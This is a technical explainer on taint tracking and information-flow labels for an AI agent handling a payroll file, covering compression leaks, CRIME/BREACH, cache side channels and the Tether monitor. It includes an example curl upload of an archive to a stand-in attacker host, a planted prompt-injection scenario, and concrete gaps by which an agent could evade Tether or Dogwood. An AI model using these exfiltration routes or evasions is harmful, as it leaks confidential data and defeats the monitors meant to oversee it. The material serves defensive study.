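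Ana's company does not need this much detail. If payroll.csv has one label and everything else in the program is public, the tracker needs only two labels. Labels can still spread too far, but the number of distinct labels cannot grow.

### The cost on gzip

Updating marks after almost every instruction slows a program down. Clause and colleagues found that gzip took about 30 times as long under Dytan, or about 50 times as long when Dytan also followed branches. It also used about 240 times as much memory. They had written Dytan to be flexible and had not optimised it.

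Kemerlis and colleagues designed libdft for speed, with short tracking routines that Pin can insert directly between the program's instructions. It slowed a set of common utilities, including gzip, by a factor of 1.14 to about 6, with an average of 3.65. Programs that mostly read and wrote files slowed the least, and the compressor bzip2 slowed the most.

*A General Approach for Efficiently Accelerating Software-based Dynamic Data Flow Tracking* (Jee, Portokalidis and colleagues) then made libdft 1.72 times faster on average by removing redundant tracking steps, such as updates to a temporary value that the program never uses again. Compression with bzip2 took 65.5 seconds without tracking, 506 seconds under libdft and 269 seconds with the improvements.

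The Taint Rabbit instead saves time by keeping several versions of each short block of instructions and choosing between them by checking which inputs have marks. If none do, it runs a version without any tracking code. Galea and Kroening measured a slowdown of 1.3 times on gzip, compared with 6.7 and 40.5 times for two other trackers that support detailed labels. Their test file contained random data, which hardly compresses, so the result may not hold for a salary table full of repeated text.

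Despite these gains, libdft and the Taint Rabbit would still lose the label on the match length in ABABABAB, because neither marks the flags register.

### The compressor as one box

A tracker can avoid most of these difficulties by ignoring what happens inside the compressor. It treats the whole program or library function as one operation, and gives everything that comes out the join of the labels on everything that went in:

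L(output) = L(input₁) ⊔ … ⊔ L(inputₖ)

This applies Denning's rule to the compressor as a whole, so payroll.zip gets payroll.csv's label however the program uses its tables and branches. A Base64 encoder's output likewise gets its input's label, whether the encoder looks up its characters or computes them.

Existing trackers can already do this. With libdft, a developer can attach code to a chosen function and mark any number of bytes in memory, so the tool could mark the compressor's output as soon as the function finishes. *Sdft* (2021) goes further and uses summarised rules instead of tracking each instruction. A summary can be more exact than the join of all input labels, but someone has to work out what the function does, and a mistake could let a label disappear.

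The box rule doesn't track which inputs produced which parts of the output. When the agent puts payroll.csv and a public holiday calendar into the same archive, the whole archive gets the payroll label. If the agent later unpacks it and the tracker treats the decompressor as a box too, the calendar comes out with that label, and the agent can't send it to Carol.

This loss usually makes no difference to an export check on the whole archive. DEFLATE is lossless, so the decompressor can restore every byte. Changing any byte of payroll.csv must therefore change the compressed output, so the output as a whole depends on all of them. Even a perfect tracker with a separate label for every bit would have to join those labels when the agent attached the archive to an email. The result would be the same as under the box rule, and the check would block the email to Carol.

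The box has to include everything the compressor writes, such as temporary files and messages on the screen. The tracker also has to identify a program as a compressor before it can apply a rule for one. An agent that writes its own Base64 encoder never calls the library function that the developer marked. To catch that, the tracker has to draw the box around the running program, whatever it does.

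## Which transformed data still counts as sensitive

If a system labels everything a program writes after reading payroll.csv as sensitive, it correctly labels payroll.zip, but it also labels the average salary of 500 people. A company that wants to release results like that average needs a test for which ones are still sensitive. Three tests are plausible, and they often give different answers.

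Under the dependence test, an output is sensitive if changing the secret, with everything else fixed, could change the output. This test applies noninterference to a single output, and labels approximate the test's result.

Under the recovery test, an output is sensitive if the recipient could use it to work out the secret or any part of the secret worth protecting. The result depends on what the recipient already knows and how much computing power they have.

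Under the quantity test, an output is sensitive if it reveals more than an agreed number of bits. Suppose Ana's company sets the limit at 16.

The message "Ben earns more than 100,000" is sensitive only under the dependence test, since it doesn't give Ben's salary and reveals at most one bit. The quantity test handles other outputs badly. A four-digit PIN holds about 13.3 bits, so a program could reveal all of it and stay under the limit. If every salary is below a million dollars, the average over 500 people can reveal up to 19.9 bits, which is over the limit, even though nobody could work out Ben's salary from the average alone.

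### Counting bits

These numbers come from quantitative information flow, the branch of the field that measures how much a program leaks. It starts from entropy, which expresses how uncertain an observer is about a secret S before seeing any output:

H(S) = −Σ p(s) log₂ p(s)

If N values are equally likely, this comes to log₂ N. A random four-digit PIN has 10,000 possible values, so its entropy is log₂ 10,000 ≈ 13.29 bits. *Quantifying Dynamic Leakage* (2019) defines the leak as the mutual information between the secret and the output O, which is the uncertainty that the output removes:

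I(S; O) = H(S) − H(S | O)

Suppose a program prints the last digit of the PIN. An observer who sees a 7 still has 1,000 candidates, which leaves log₂ 1,000 ≈ 9.97 bits unknown. The program has therefore revealed 13.29 − 9.97 = 3.32 bits. This equals log₂ 10, because the program had ten equally likely outputs.

A program with N possible outputs can reveal at most log₂ N bits on average, however the secrets are distributed. The most it can reveal is called its channel capacity. *Model Counting Modulo Theories* (2015) credits this limit to Malacaria and Chen, and to Smith, who reached it in 2009 with a different measure of entropy. An output of k bits has at most 2ᵏ possible values, so it reveals at most k bits. Applying this bound doesn't require looking inside the program. The output also can't reveal more than the secret contains, so even a 256-bit output computed from a four-digit PIN reveals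 at most 13.29 bits.

A program that reveals little on average can still reveal the whole secret in a single run. Suppose the program prints only whether the PIN is 1234. Averaged over all PINs, this reveals about 0.0015 bits, but one time in 10,000 the answer is "yes" and the observer learns the whole PIN. *Quantifying Dynamic Leakage* calls the amount revealed by one particular output dynamic leakage. *On the Compositionality of Dynamic Leakage and Its Application to the Quantification* (2019) proposes measuring it by narrowing the secret to the inputs that could have produced the output. For "yes", only one input remains, with probability 1/10,000, so the one-bit answer reveals −log₂(1/10,000) ≈ 13.29 bits.

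The k-bit bound does guarantee a limit under Smith's measure, which is based on the observer's chance of guessing the secret at the first attempt. An output of k bits can multiply that chance, averaged over all outcomes, by at most 2ᵏ. For the PIN, the one-bit yes-or-no answer doubles the average chance from 1 in 10,000 to 2 in 10,000.

A company that relies on the bound has to count everything the recipient observes, including whether a message arrives. It also has to keep a running total across outputs, because ten outputs of 16 bits each can reveal 160 bits, enough for eight salaries.

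### Measuring the flow through a program

An output's length often greatly overstates how much it reveals, but the exact amount is hard to compute. *Quantifying Dynamic Leakage* points out that computing it is at least as hard as checking noninterference, because noninterference means a leak of zero bits.

McCamant and Ernst (2008), in *Quantitative information flow as network flow capacity*, compute an upper bound on how much secret information a particular run of a program can reveal. They model the run as a network of pipes from the secret input to the output. Each value the program computes is a pipe whose capacity is the number of bits the value can hold. The maximum flow through the network bounds the leak. It equals the capacity of the narrowest set of pipes that separates input from output, so the method also shows where the bottleneck is. McCamant and Ernst account for branches and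 pointer operations, and they tried their tool, Flowcheck, on real programs, three of them with more than 250,000 lines of code.

A short C program shows how this differs from tainting. It counts the full stops and question marks in a secret text, then prints the more common mark as many times as it occurred. If it prints eight full stops, taint tracking marks all 64 output bits. Flowcheck gives a bound of 9 bits, one for which mark is printed and eight for the count.

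The tool's developers also ran it on the compressor bzip2, using the digits of π written out as English words as the secret input. Whenever bzip2 shortened the text, the measured flow matched the size of the compressed output. If a company set its limit as a share of the original file's size, the limit would therefore be unreliable for compressible files, because an archive a tenth as long can contain the whole file. Measuring a 2.5-megabyte input took about an hour and a half.

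It is harder to judge by eye how much information a lossy transformation preserves. MIT CSAIL's *Quantitative information flow measurement* describes a test on a photograph of a face, altered in four ways so that none of the results was immediately recognisable. Flowcheck's bound on the information preserved was below 1% of the original for two of the images and the full amount for the other two. One of the latter two used a swirl effect, which a viewer can largely undo by swirling the image the other way.

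Even 1% of an image can be a lot of data. A patch of 100 by 100 pixels with 24 bits per pixel holds 240,000 bits, and 1% of that would be enough for 120 six-digit salaries. The bound doesn't show which details those bits describe. McCamant's *Quantitative Information Flow Measurement* outlines a later project that uses fast capacity bounds to find where it is worth running model counting, a slower method that counts the solutions to a logical formula describing the program's behaviour.

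### A label for each case

The table applies the three tests to outputs that Ana's agent might produce. It assumes 500 salaries, all whole-dollar amounts below a million.

| Output | Depends on the secret? | Can the recipient recover the secret? | Bits revealed | Defensible label |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lossless archive of payroll.csv | Yes | Yes | All | {Ana, Ben} |
| Base64 copy | Yes | Yes | All | {Ana, Ben} |
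| 64 × 64 greyscale thumbnail of a payroll screenshot | Yes | Perhaps in part | Up to 32,768 | {Ana, Ben} |
| Ciphertext, key kept inside | Yes | No, apart from the length | Nearly all, if computing is free | Public; the key stays {Ana, Ben} |
| Ciphertext, key sent along | Yes | Yes | All | {Ana, Ben} |
| 256-bit hash of a long document | Yes | Only by guessing the document | Up to 256 | The document's label |
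| 256-bit hash of a PIN | Yes | Yes | Up to 13.3 | The PIN's label |
| Average salary of 500 people, to the dollar | Yes | Not from this average alone | Up to 19.9 | {Ana, Ben} until someone approves its release |
| Exact average of two salaries | Yes | Yes, if they know one of the two | Up to 20.9 | {Ana, Ben} |
| File name or timestamp set before the agent read payroll.csv | No | No | 0 | Its own label |
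| File name or timestamp chosen afterwards | Possibly | Possibly | Up to its length | {Ana, Ben} |
| File size | Yes | Not from one size | log₂ of the number of possible sizes | {Ana, Ben} |
| Archive of payroll.csv and a public brochure | Yes | Yes | All | {Ana, Ben} |
| The brochure after extraction | No | No | 0 | Public |

All three tests agree on the archive and the Base64 copy, since the recipient can reverse both.

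A short secret may survive in a thumbnail despite the lost detail. The security firm Bishop Fox, which published *Never, Ever, Ever Use Pixelation for Redacting Text*, built a tool that turns pixelated text back into readable text, and it redacts its own reports only with black bars. Black bars can fail too. In *Residual information of redacted images hidden in the compression artifacts*, Ho and Chang (2008) studied pictures that had been compressed, redacted and compressed again. If the second compression preserved more detail than the first, traces of the first could show which of several candidate texts had been redacted. They call the requirements for this stringent. Still, a lossy copy should keep its label unless someone has checked what it lost, even if a person can't read the secret in it.

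#### Encryption

The tests differ most on ciphertext. Changing a salary changes the ciphertext, so the ciphertext is sensitive under the dependence test. But Carol has no practical way to read the salary without the key, so the ciphertext is not sensitive under the recovery test.

The quantity test measures information without regard to the computing effort needed to extract it. If each salary were equally likely to be any amount in the range, 500 salaries would hold about 9,966 bits. Someone with unlimited computing power could try every 256-bit key, so the ciphertext leaves at most 256 bits of uncertainty and reveals the other 9,710. A one-time pad, which uses a random key as long as the file, would reveal nothing except the length. Few companies use one-time pads, and the recovery test gives a more sensible answer for ordinary encryption.

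Lowering the ciphertext's label is safe only if the key keeps the payroll label. If the agent sends the ciphertext on Monday and tries to send the key on Tuesday, the export rule must stop the second message. Carol's planted instruction could also tell the agent which password to put on payroll.zip, and she could then open the archive without anyone sending her the password. The label should therefore come off only when a trusted service generates the key at random and keeps it out of the agent's reach. An archive that the agent encrypted itself should keep the label {Ana, Ben}.

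#### Hashes

A cryptographic hash function turns any file into a short fingerprint (256 bits for SHA-256) that can't practically be reversed. But a recipient who gets the hash of a four-digit PIN can use an ordinary computer to hash all 10,000 possible PINs and find the match in a fraction of a second. Adding random data to the PIN before hashing doesn't help if the recipient gets that data too. Mixing in a secret key would help, but the key would need the same protection as an encryption key.

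A long document's hash is usually safe from this kind of guessing, because nobody can list every possible long document. But if Carol already had a copy of payroll.csv missing only Ben's salary, she would have at most a million candidates to check. Even when she can't narrow the document down that far, the hash lets her confirm that a file she already has is the same one. The document's label is a sensible default for the hash, and the company can lower the hash's label if outsiders couldn't reconstruct the document.

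#### Averages

If Dana receives the exact average of her salary and Ben's, she can double it and subtract her own salary to get Ben's. If the average covers 500 people, she can't work out Ben's salary from her own salary and the average alone, so a company may reasonably decide to publish it.

A second average can undo that protection. If the company publishes an average a for 500 people and then an average b after hiring one more, the new employee earns 501b − 500a, provided nobody else's pay has changed. If both averages are rounded to the nearest dollar, the result is off by at most about $500 and is still a good estimate, but rounding to the nearest thousand can put it off by about $500,000, which makes it nearly useless. Whether an average is safe to release therefore depends on earlier releases, which a label on a single number cannot take into account.

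#### Names, sizes and timestamps

The name payroll.csv existed before the agent read any salaries, so it reveals nothing about them. The name may still have a label if it is sensitive in itself, as layoffs-march.csv would be. Once the agent has read the file, it can put a salary into the name of a new file or into a modification time, which programs can set freely. The zip format stores that time in 32 bits, which is enough for a six-digit salary because that takes 20.

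A file's size depends on its contents even if nobody has tampered with it, so the size of payroll.csv gives a rough count of the employees. Blocking every output whose size Carol could observe would be impractical, so a company will probably release ordinary sizes and guard against cases where a size reveals more.

#### Mixed archives

An archive that contains payroll.csv and a public brochure needs the payroll label, but the brochure extracted from it does not. The brochure's bytes don't depend on what Ben earns, so it can be public even under the dependence test. The box rule would still give the brochure the payroll label.

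A system can correct this by comparing the extracted file with the public original and restoring the Public label if every byte matches. This works for both zip archives, which compress each file separately, and .tar.gz archives, which compress the files as one stream. But the agent's choice of which public brochure to extract can still reveal something about Ben's salary, just as its choice of tool can.

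### Compressed size, CRIME and BREACH

Size becomes a more serious leak when data is compressed before it is encrypted. *Compression and Information Leakage of Plaintext* (Kelsey, 2002) explains that encryption is meant to hide everything about a text except its length. Compression makes that length depend on the content, because repetitive text shrinks more than varied text. An observer who sees only the encrypted size therefore learns something about the content.

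Kelsey had raised the problem a year earlier in *Compression side channel*, a thread on a cryptography mailing list. He considered messages that combine a secret with text an outsider can choose. In his informal trials with random PINs, the correct PIN was among his 20 best guesses about 60–70% of the time. Danisch (2001) replied in the thread that the mistake was compressing the secret and the outsider's text together.

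Some engineers think compression helps privacy. In *Disabling compression in OpenPGP*, a discussion on a standards mailing list, one participant argues that it turns recognisable text into something close to random. Another answers that an observer who knows the original length and measures the compressed ciphertext still learns something about the content. Both can be right, since compression can make the bytes look random while their number still reveals how well the text compressed.

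CRIME (2012) and BREACH (2013) are attacks on web traffic that use this principle. A web page may contain both a secret and text from the requested address, which an attacker can influence. If the two share a string, DEFLATE replaces the repeat with a match and the compressed page gets shorter. Encryption hides the page's content but not the change in length, and an attacker can work out the secret from many such changes. CRIME exploited compression in TLS, the protocol that encrypts web connections, while BREACH exploited compression of the pages themselves. The designers of TLS responded by removing compression from the protocol.

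The same conditions can arise in Ana's office. Her agent might put payroll data and a paragraph from Carol's email into one report, compress it, encrypt it and send it to Ben. The export rule allows this because Ben is a permitted reader. If Carol can measure the encrypted traffic, she can compare the sizes of reports that contain different emails from her. One size would tell her very little, so both the recovery test and a 16-bit limit would probably let it through, but she could learn more about the payroll data by comparing many.

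### Using taint to control the compressor

Danisch's remedy requires knowing which text is secret before compression starts, and taint tracking can supply that information. *Debreach* (Paulsen, Sung and colleagues, 2019) applies taint tracking to PHP web applications. A developer lists the functions that fetch sensitive data, such as the one that reads an address book. Debreach then analyses the code to find every statement that could print such data to a page, and rewrites the program to put markers around the data when printing it.

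A modified DEFLATE compressor removes the markers. It never replaces sensitive text with a reference to earlier text, and never refers back to sensitive text from elsewhere. The rest of the page compresses normally. The output is valid DEFLATE, so browsers need no changes.

Paulsen and colleagues state the guarantee as a form of noninterference. Let R(X, S) be the length of the output of the matching stage, for public strings X and secret strings S. Then

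for all X, S, S′ with |sᵢ| = |s′ᵢ| for every i: R(X, S) = R(X, S′)

Changing what the secrets contain therefore does not affect that length, although changing how long they are may. The guarantee does not cover DEFLATE's code table. Characters in the secret still influence the table's bit patterns, so the final size can vary slightly with the secret. Paulsen and colleagues accept this variation because they know of no reported attack that uses it.

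Branches caused over-tainting in Debreach, as in other trackers. Debreach therefore ignores a branch that only checks a variable's type or length, or compares it with a fixed value in the code. It still follows a branch that compares secret text with text from outside and then prints the outside text, since the printed text would match the secret. If Debreach hadn't ignored the first kind of branch, it would have reported hundreds of harmless print statements.

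Paulsen and colleagues tested Debreach on five applications with 145,000 lines of code in total. The analysis took less than three minutes for each, and the rewritten PHP code ran less than 3% slower on 22 of 25 pages. On average, Debreach compressed pages 15.6% better than SafeDeflate, an earlier defence that classifies text as sensitive based on the characters in it. Its compression came within 2.5% of that of a version whose markers they had corrected by hand. They also measured the leak in a webmail program and a database tool. Once an observer knew the first three characters of a secret, a correct guess at the next one made the compressed page measurably smaller without Debreach, but never with it.

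This approach suits Ana's agent better than a ban on compression because the tracker's labels on the payroll data and Carol's email already identify which text to keep apart. Compressing the two separately would be even simpler, since the agent could use an unmodified compressor, but text that appears in both would compress less well.

### Leaks while the compressor runs

Like compressed size, a compressor's memory accesses can reveal the contents of the data. A compressor uses its input to choose which table entries to read and write, and those choices affect the processor's cache, a small, fast memory that programs on the same machine often share. Another program can time its own memory accesses to work out roughly which entries the compressor used.

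*ZipChannel*, by Minkin and Kasikci, presents TaintChannel, a tool for finding these leaks. It marks every input byte, follows the marks through copying and arithmetic, and reports each place where marked data determines a memory address. Many trackers lose a label at these lookups, but TaintChannel doesn't need to carry the mark through them because its purpose is to find them. It ignores branches to avoid marking too much data.

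The tool found such accesses in implementations of all three major families of compression algorithm:

| Algorithm | Program | What selects the address | What an observer of the accesses could recover |
|---|---|---|---|
| LZ77 | zlib | A number computed from three consecutive bytes | A quarter of the input directly; nearly all of it if the text is lower-case letters |
| LZ78 | ncompress | The next byte combined with a dictionary entry | All of it, after trying eight options for the first byte |
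| BWT | bzip2 | A pair of neighbouring bytes | All of it |

LZ77 is the matching stage of DEFLATE, so payroll.zip belongs in the first row. LZ78 builds a numbered dictionary of strings as it reads. The Burrows–Wheeler transform (BWT) rearranges the text to group similar characters.

The last column assumes an observer who can locate every memory access to within a 64-byte block. Minkin and Kasikci checked the ncompress result with a simulated record of accesses. For bzip2, they carried out a real attack on a compressor inside an SGX enclave, an area of memory that Intel processors protect even from the operating system. They recovered more than 99% of the bits in 10 kilobytes of random data in under 30 seconds, but the attacker had unusual control over the machine. In a more ordinary setting, with two applications on one system, they could often tell which of 21 known files bzip2 was compressing,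 but they did not recover the contents.

Carol can't do any of this from her mailbox, because she would need a program running on the machine that compresses payroll.csv. If she had one, a check at the email tool wouldn't help, since the salaries could leak without the agent sending the archive. Minkin and Kasikci suggest, but did not build, compressors whose running time and memory accesses don't depend on the input, which is already a goal in cryptographic software. Until such compressors exist, the company's practical option is to compress sensitive files on a machine that runs no untrusted programs.

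## Following labels through files, archives and shell commands

Programs cannot open files or send data by themselves. They have to ask the operating system through a system call, such as `read` to get a file's contents or `write` to store something. A tracker that watches these calls can treat any running program, or process, as one box, including a Base64 encoder that the agent wrote a minute ago. It needs two rules. For a process p and a file f,

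read: L(p) becomes L(p) ⊔ L(f)

write: L(f) becomes L(f) ⊔ L(p)

When a compressor reads payroll.csv, its process gets the label {Ana, Ben} and passes it to payroll.zip. Labeling the whole process is less precise than tracking each byte, but the label can't be lost at a table lookup.

### HiStar, Flume and TaintDroid

Operating-system researchers built such trackers long before AI agents existed. *Making Information Flow Explicit in HiStar* (Zeldovich, Boyd-Wickizer and colleagues, 2006) describes an operating system whose kernel, or core, enforces information-flow control and is the only fully trusted code. HiStar has no superuser, the account that can override restrictions on an ordinary Unix machine. Almost all of its Unix-like environment runs as an untrusted library, so a bug there should not let labelled data out. In 2007, Krohn and colleagues published Flume, which applies the same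 kind of control to standard operating-system abstractions such as processes and pipes.

A process that serves several people can collect too many labels. *HiStar*, a set of University of Washington course notes on the system, gives the example of a web server that reads Alice's files and may then have Alice's secrecy tag in its own label. If the same process then answers Bob, the reply has Alice's tag even if it contains none of her data. Running a separate process for each user avoids this.

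TaintDroid, which Enck and colleagues built for Android phones, modifies an app's code so that every variable and every message between processes has a tag, and it checks the tags at outgoing network connections (*Quire*, 2011). Each file has only one tag, however, and *Android Inter-App Communication Threats and Detection Techniques* (2016) lists the resulting false positives among TaintDroid's limitations. The same survey reports a 14% slowdown on a processor-heavy test and notes that TaintDroid follows only data flows.

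*Intra-Library Collusion* (2017) reports that Enck and colleagues found 68 leaks in 20 of the 30 apps they studied. Half of the apps sent the phone's location to advertising servers without the user's consent, in some cases without showing an advertisement. These results, like Staicu and colleagues' results on JavaScript, come from existing software and may not apply to code that an agent writes to evade the tracker.

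### Running each command on trial

Tether, the monitor that Sistla and colleagues built at Google DeepMind, Google and two universities, applies file-level tracking to an agent's shell commands. The text of a command often doesn't show what it will do. `python report.py` might print a table or post payroll.csv to Carol's website, and running the command to find out may leak the salaries.

Tether therefore runs the command on trial:

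1. It places a disposable layer over the file system. The command sees the normal files, but any changes go into a temporary directory.
2. A tool called strace records the system calls of the command and of the processes it starts.
3. A local proxy holds each outgoing network request.
4. A component called Isolate translates the record into abstract actions, such as "copy this file to that one" or "upload this file to that host".
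5. The policy monitor checks the actions. If it allows them, Tether makes the file changes permanent and forwards the requests. Otherwise it discards both.

When a running command makes a network request, the proxy holds the request while the monitor evaluates everything the command has done up to that point.

Isolate keeps a set of source files for each process. Reading a file adds it to the set, and the set passes through pipes to later processes. When a process writes to a file, Isolate reports a plain write if the set is empty, a copy if it contains one file, and a concatenation if it contains several. The command `cat payroll.csv | gzip | base64 > notes.txt` starts three programs, but Isolate reports the result as a copy of payroll.csv to notes.txt.

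This is deliberately an overestimate, because a program may write something unrelated to what it read. Isolate does leave out the system files that every program reads when it starts, because counting them would make almost every copy look like a concatenation.

### The label rules

Tether stores a label σ(f) for the contents of each file f. It also stores the context label T, which covers what the agent has seen. The main rules are:

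| Action | When Isolate reports it | Effect on labels |
|---|---|---|
| Read f | Data from f reaches the agent, for example on the terminal | T becomes T ⊔ σ(f) |
| Write d | A process with no source files changes d | σ(d) becomes σ(d) ⊔ T |
| Copy s to d | A process with one source file overwrites d | σ(d) becomes σ(s) |
| Concatenate s₁, …, sₙ into d | A process with several source files writes d | σ(d) becomes σ(s₁) ⊔ … ⊔ σ(sₙ) |
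| Upload s to a host | A process that has read s sends data to the host | No change, but the policy can check T ⊔ σ(s) first |

The full rules for copying and concatenating also join the destination folder's label with the labels of the input files, so a company can make everything in one folder sensitive.

A copy replaces d's old label because the old contents are gone. An append keeps the old contents, so Isolate also counts d as a source and reports a concatenation. A plain write gets T because the text probably came from the agent itself, for example when it writes a sentence to a file with `echo`.

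Copying a file does not change T. Ana's agent can compress payroll.csv for Ben without any salary appearing in its context, and then upload an unrelated public file. If the agent instead prints payroll.csv to the terminal, T rises to the payroll label and the policy restricts every later upload.

### The payroll archive under Tether

The policy in Sistla and colleagues' experiments uses four levels, Public ⊑ Internal ⊑ Sensitive ⊑ Secret. Suppose payroll.csv is Sensitive, a holiday calendar is Public, and the agent runs three commands:

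```
gzip -c payroll.csv > scratch/payroll.gz                   # (1)
tar cf scratch/pack.tar scratch/payroll.gz holidays.txt    # (2)
curl --data-binary @scratch/pack.tar carol.example         # (3)
```

In command (1), gzip reads one file and writes another. Isolate reports a copy, and payroll.gz becomes Sensitive. In command (2), tar reads two files and packs them into one, which is a concatenation:

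σ(pack.tar) = Sensitive ⊔ Public = Sensitive

In command (3), curl reads pack.tar and tries to send data to Carol's host, so Isolate reports an upload. The policy lets data go to an outside host only if T ⊔ σ(pack.tar) ⊑ Internal. The combined label here is Sensitive, which is stricter than Internal, so the monitor denies the upload and the proxy drops the request.

If the agent had instead written one Python script that read payroll.csv, compressed it in memory and sent it, no archive would have appeared on disk. Isolate would have reported an upload of payroll.csv itself, because the script had read that file before contacting the host.

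Tether's upload rule identifies destinations by network address and domain name. If the agent emails the archive through the company's own mail server, the host is the same whether the recipient is Ben or Carol. The email tool would still have to apply the export rule to the actual recipients, and it would need the label from Tether to do so.

#### File names and sizes

Tether labels a file's name and other metadata separately from its contents. When a process creates a file, the metadata gets the join of T, the folder's label and the content labels of every file the process has already read. For example, if a script reads Ben's salary and then creates an empty file called 150000.txt, the file's name is labelled Sensitive. If the agent then lists the folder, it reads the name, and T becomes Sensitive too.

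Renaming an existing file counts as a copy followed by a deletion, so calling the archive beach.jpg does not remove its label.

The metadata rule has a gap when the destination file already exists, because a copy changes the label on the file's contents but not the label on its size. Under the published rules, the agent could compress payroll.csv over an old public file and look up the new size without raising T. A single size reveals little, but an agent that chose what to compress alongside the salaries could learn more by repeating the measurement, as in the CRIME attack.

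### Labels compared with a log of past actions

A monitor could also keep a log of the agent's actions and search it before each upload, as Amazon's rule system Dogwood does. Sistla and colleagues wrote Dogwood rules for their inventory-file example and found that each rule catches only a fixed number of steps. For example, one rule detects the upload of a direct copy, but detecting a copy of a copy takes another rule.

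The number of patterns grows quickly with the length of the chain. With m kinds of action, covering every chain of up to k steps takes m + m² + … + mᵏ patterns. For copying, compressing and renaming, chains of up to four steps need 3 + 9 + 27 + 81 = 120 patterns, and an agent could evade them all by adding a fifth step. Dogwood also looks back at most 24 hours by default, so an agent could evade the patterns by copying the file and waiting a day.

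Strands Box, Amazon's sandbox for Dogwood, records file reads and writes for commands built into its own shell, but not for `tar`, which runs separately. A rule about archives therefore has to match the text of the `tar` command. A broader rule could forbid uploading any file written after the agent opened the inventory, but it would also block copies of public files. With labels, a single upload rule covers chains of commands of any length and still allows uploads of those public copies.

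Sistla and colleagues made this comparison without running Dogwood on their benchmarks, because the sandbox does not support arbitrary Linux programs.

### Results on recorded agent runs

Sistla and colleagues tested Tether on two collections of recorded agent runs. MonitoringBenchHonest covers system administration in 88 Linux containers. LinuxArena has more than 340 software-engineering tasks in 10 simulated production environments. In the benign runs, an agent only did its assigned task. In the harmful ones it also pursued a harmful side task. Sistla and colleagues replayed the commands inside Tether and counted the runs it blocked. These figures cover only runs in which every action took place in the foreground and was of a kind that Tether models:

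| Test set | Harmful runs blocked | Benign runs wrongly blocked |
|---|---|---|
| MonitoringBenchHonest | 199 of 199 | 5 of 218 (2.3%) |
| LinuxArena | 145 of 145 | 69 of 1,372 (5.0%) |
| Both | 344 of 344 | 74 of 1,590 (4.7%) |

In 50 of the 74 wrongly blocked runs, the agent edited a protected system file, such as the list of user accounts, although this wasn't part of the task. In another 7, it contacted a host that wasn't declared in the task description. Sistla and colleagues consider these denials reasonable and suggest that a later version could ask the user instead.

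The other 17 show a limit of tracking system calls. A command such as `grep -r` searches every file in a folder, including sensitive ones. Isolate detects that the process read them, but not whether the search used anything from them. Ana's agent could search a shared folder for "holiday", open payroll.csv along the way and then be unable to upload anything.

Tether was also compared with the Auto Mode of Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, in which a language model judges each command. With Claude Sonnet 5 as the judge and the default settings, Auto Mode caught 91.6% of harmful runs and blocked 9.7% of benign ones. With Tether's policy given to the judge in writing, it blocked 3.5% of benign runs, fewer than Tether, but missed 37 of the 344 harmful ones. Neither version detected attacks hidden inside scripts.

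A company that writes a new policy may see a higher false-positive rate. Sistla and colleagues refined their policy by running it on the benchmark traces and changing rules that blocked too much, with help from a language model. They then used the same rules for every task, but set the labels and permitted hosts for each task from its description. Ana's company would have to do similar work for its own folders and services.

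Even 4.7% could be inconvenient, because attacks are rare. If one run in a thousand were harmful, Tether would stop that run and about 47 harmless ones. Replaying recorded commands also does not show whether, after a denial, a live agent would have found a permitted way to finish its task or an attacker would have found a new way to leak the file.

The perfect score on harmful runs applies to the chosen policy as a whole. Some of its 24 rules protect system files or restrict administrator rights, so not all 344 runs were attempts to send out data.

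Sistla and colleagues also proved properties of the policy in Lean 4, a programming language with machine-checked proofs. For example, if a permitted run starts without Secret data in the agent's context, none ever enters the context. The proofs cover sequences of abstract actions, so they hold for real commands only if Isolate correctly translates system calls into these actions. Sistla and colleagues tested the translation by generating random chains of file operations whose correct labels they knew.

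### What fell outside Tether's scope

Some harm involves no forbidden flow of data. An agent that is allowed to edit a program's source code can add a harmful line, and the system calls look the same as those for a useful edit. Sistla and colleagues estimate that 28.2% of MonitoringBenchHonest runs and 22.1% of LinuxArena runs need someone or something to judge the content. They suggest combining Tether with a language model for those runs, but any guarantee would then depend on the model being right.

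Tether can't follow data that moves through databases and background processes. A database server runs outside the traced command, and uploading data to it changes no labels. In the benchmark policy, the database postgres has the label Internal but may receive Sensitive data. If the agent loaded payroll.csv into the database and then queried it, the salaries would come back labeled Internal, and the policy allows Internal data to be sent to outside hosts.

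Tether can close this route by refusing all database connections and background processes. Sistla and colleagues found that this would intercept another 36.3% of MonitoringBenchHonest runs and 71.5% of LinuxArena runs. The high LinuxArena rate suggests that the restriction would be impractical for agents that maintain real services. Sistla and colleagues propose tracking labels inside databases instead, but have not built this. Tether also blocks some faster ways of moving data, such as shared memory, that bypass the calls it traces.

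### Labels stored in office files

Tether keeps its labels in a table on the machine it monitors, so they do not travel with a file. Microsoft Purview, a collection of data-protection products, stores the label in the file itself. A Purview label is a category such as Confidential, and applying it can encrypt the file so that only certain people can open it. According to Microsoft's documentation for SharePoint and OneDrive, its file-storage services, the label and any encryption stay with a file when someone downloads it.

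This works only for file formats that the services can read. They recognise labels on Word, Excel and PowerPoint files, but administrators have to turn on support for PDFs, MP4 videos and OneNote files separately (Office 365 for IT Pros, *SharePoint Online Expands Sensitivity Labels to OneNote and Video Files*, 2026). Other companies' software also has to look in the right part of the file. Broadcom's *Inconsistent Detection of MPIP Labels in Encrypted Co-authored Office Files (DLP 16.0.x)* describes a label that moves to a different part of an Office file when encryption and shared editing are both on, so Symantec's keyword rules may detect it in one channel and miss it in another.

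payroll.csv is plain text, with no metadata section that could hold a label. Microsoft's *Labeling improvement for non-Office files and PDF files* (2025) describes the older solution, which wraps such a file in a protective container with the extension .pfile. Anyone who wanted to edit the file had to remove the label and its protection, make the changes and apply them again. Microsoft's *Advanced label-based protection for all files on devices* (2025) offers an alternative on Windows. The file stays unencrypted while people work on it, and Endpoint DLP, Purview's monitoring software for computers, encrypts it before it leaves the device. A program can still read the unencrypted salaries and write them to a new file, which then needs a label of its own.

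#### After zipping

Suppose the salaries are in a labelled Excel file, payroll.xlsx, and the agent zips it. Zip compression is lossless, so the label is still in the file when someone extracts it. If the label encrypts the file, Carol may receive the archive but can't read the salaries. If the label is only a marking, a check at the email tool has to look inside the archive to find the label.

Microsoft's own products don't always do this. SharePoint's search can't find labelled documents in a .zip file. Microsoft's *Archive File Classification Behavior Change for Windows Endpoints* announced that Endpoint DLP would classify an archive as a single item and would not apply label-based rules to the files inside. A rule that blocks outgoing files labelled Confidential would then stop payroll.xlsx but not a zip file containing it, unless another rule recognised the contents.

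It is unclear when this change will reach every customer. The notice gave late November 2025 as the start, but in September 2026 Microsoft's roadmap entry with the same title (2026) still listed the change as in development, with general release planned for October.

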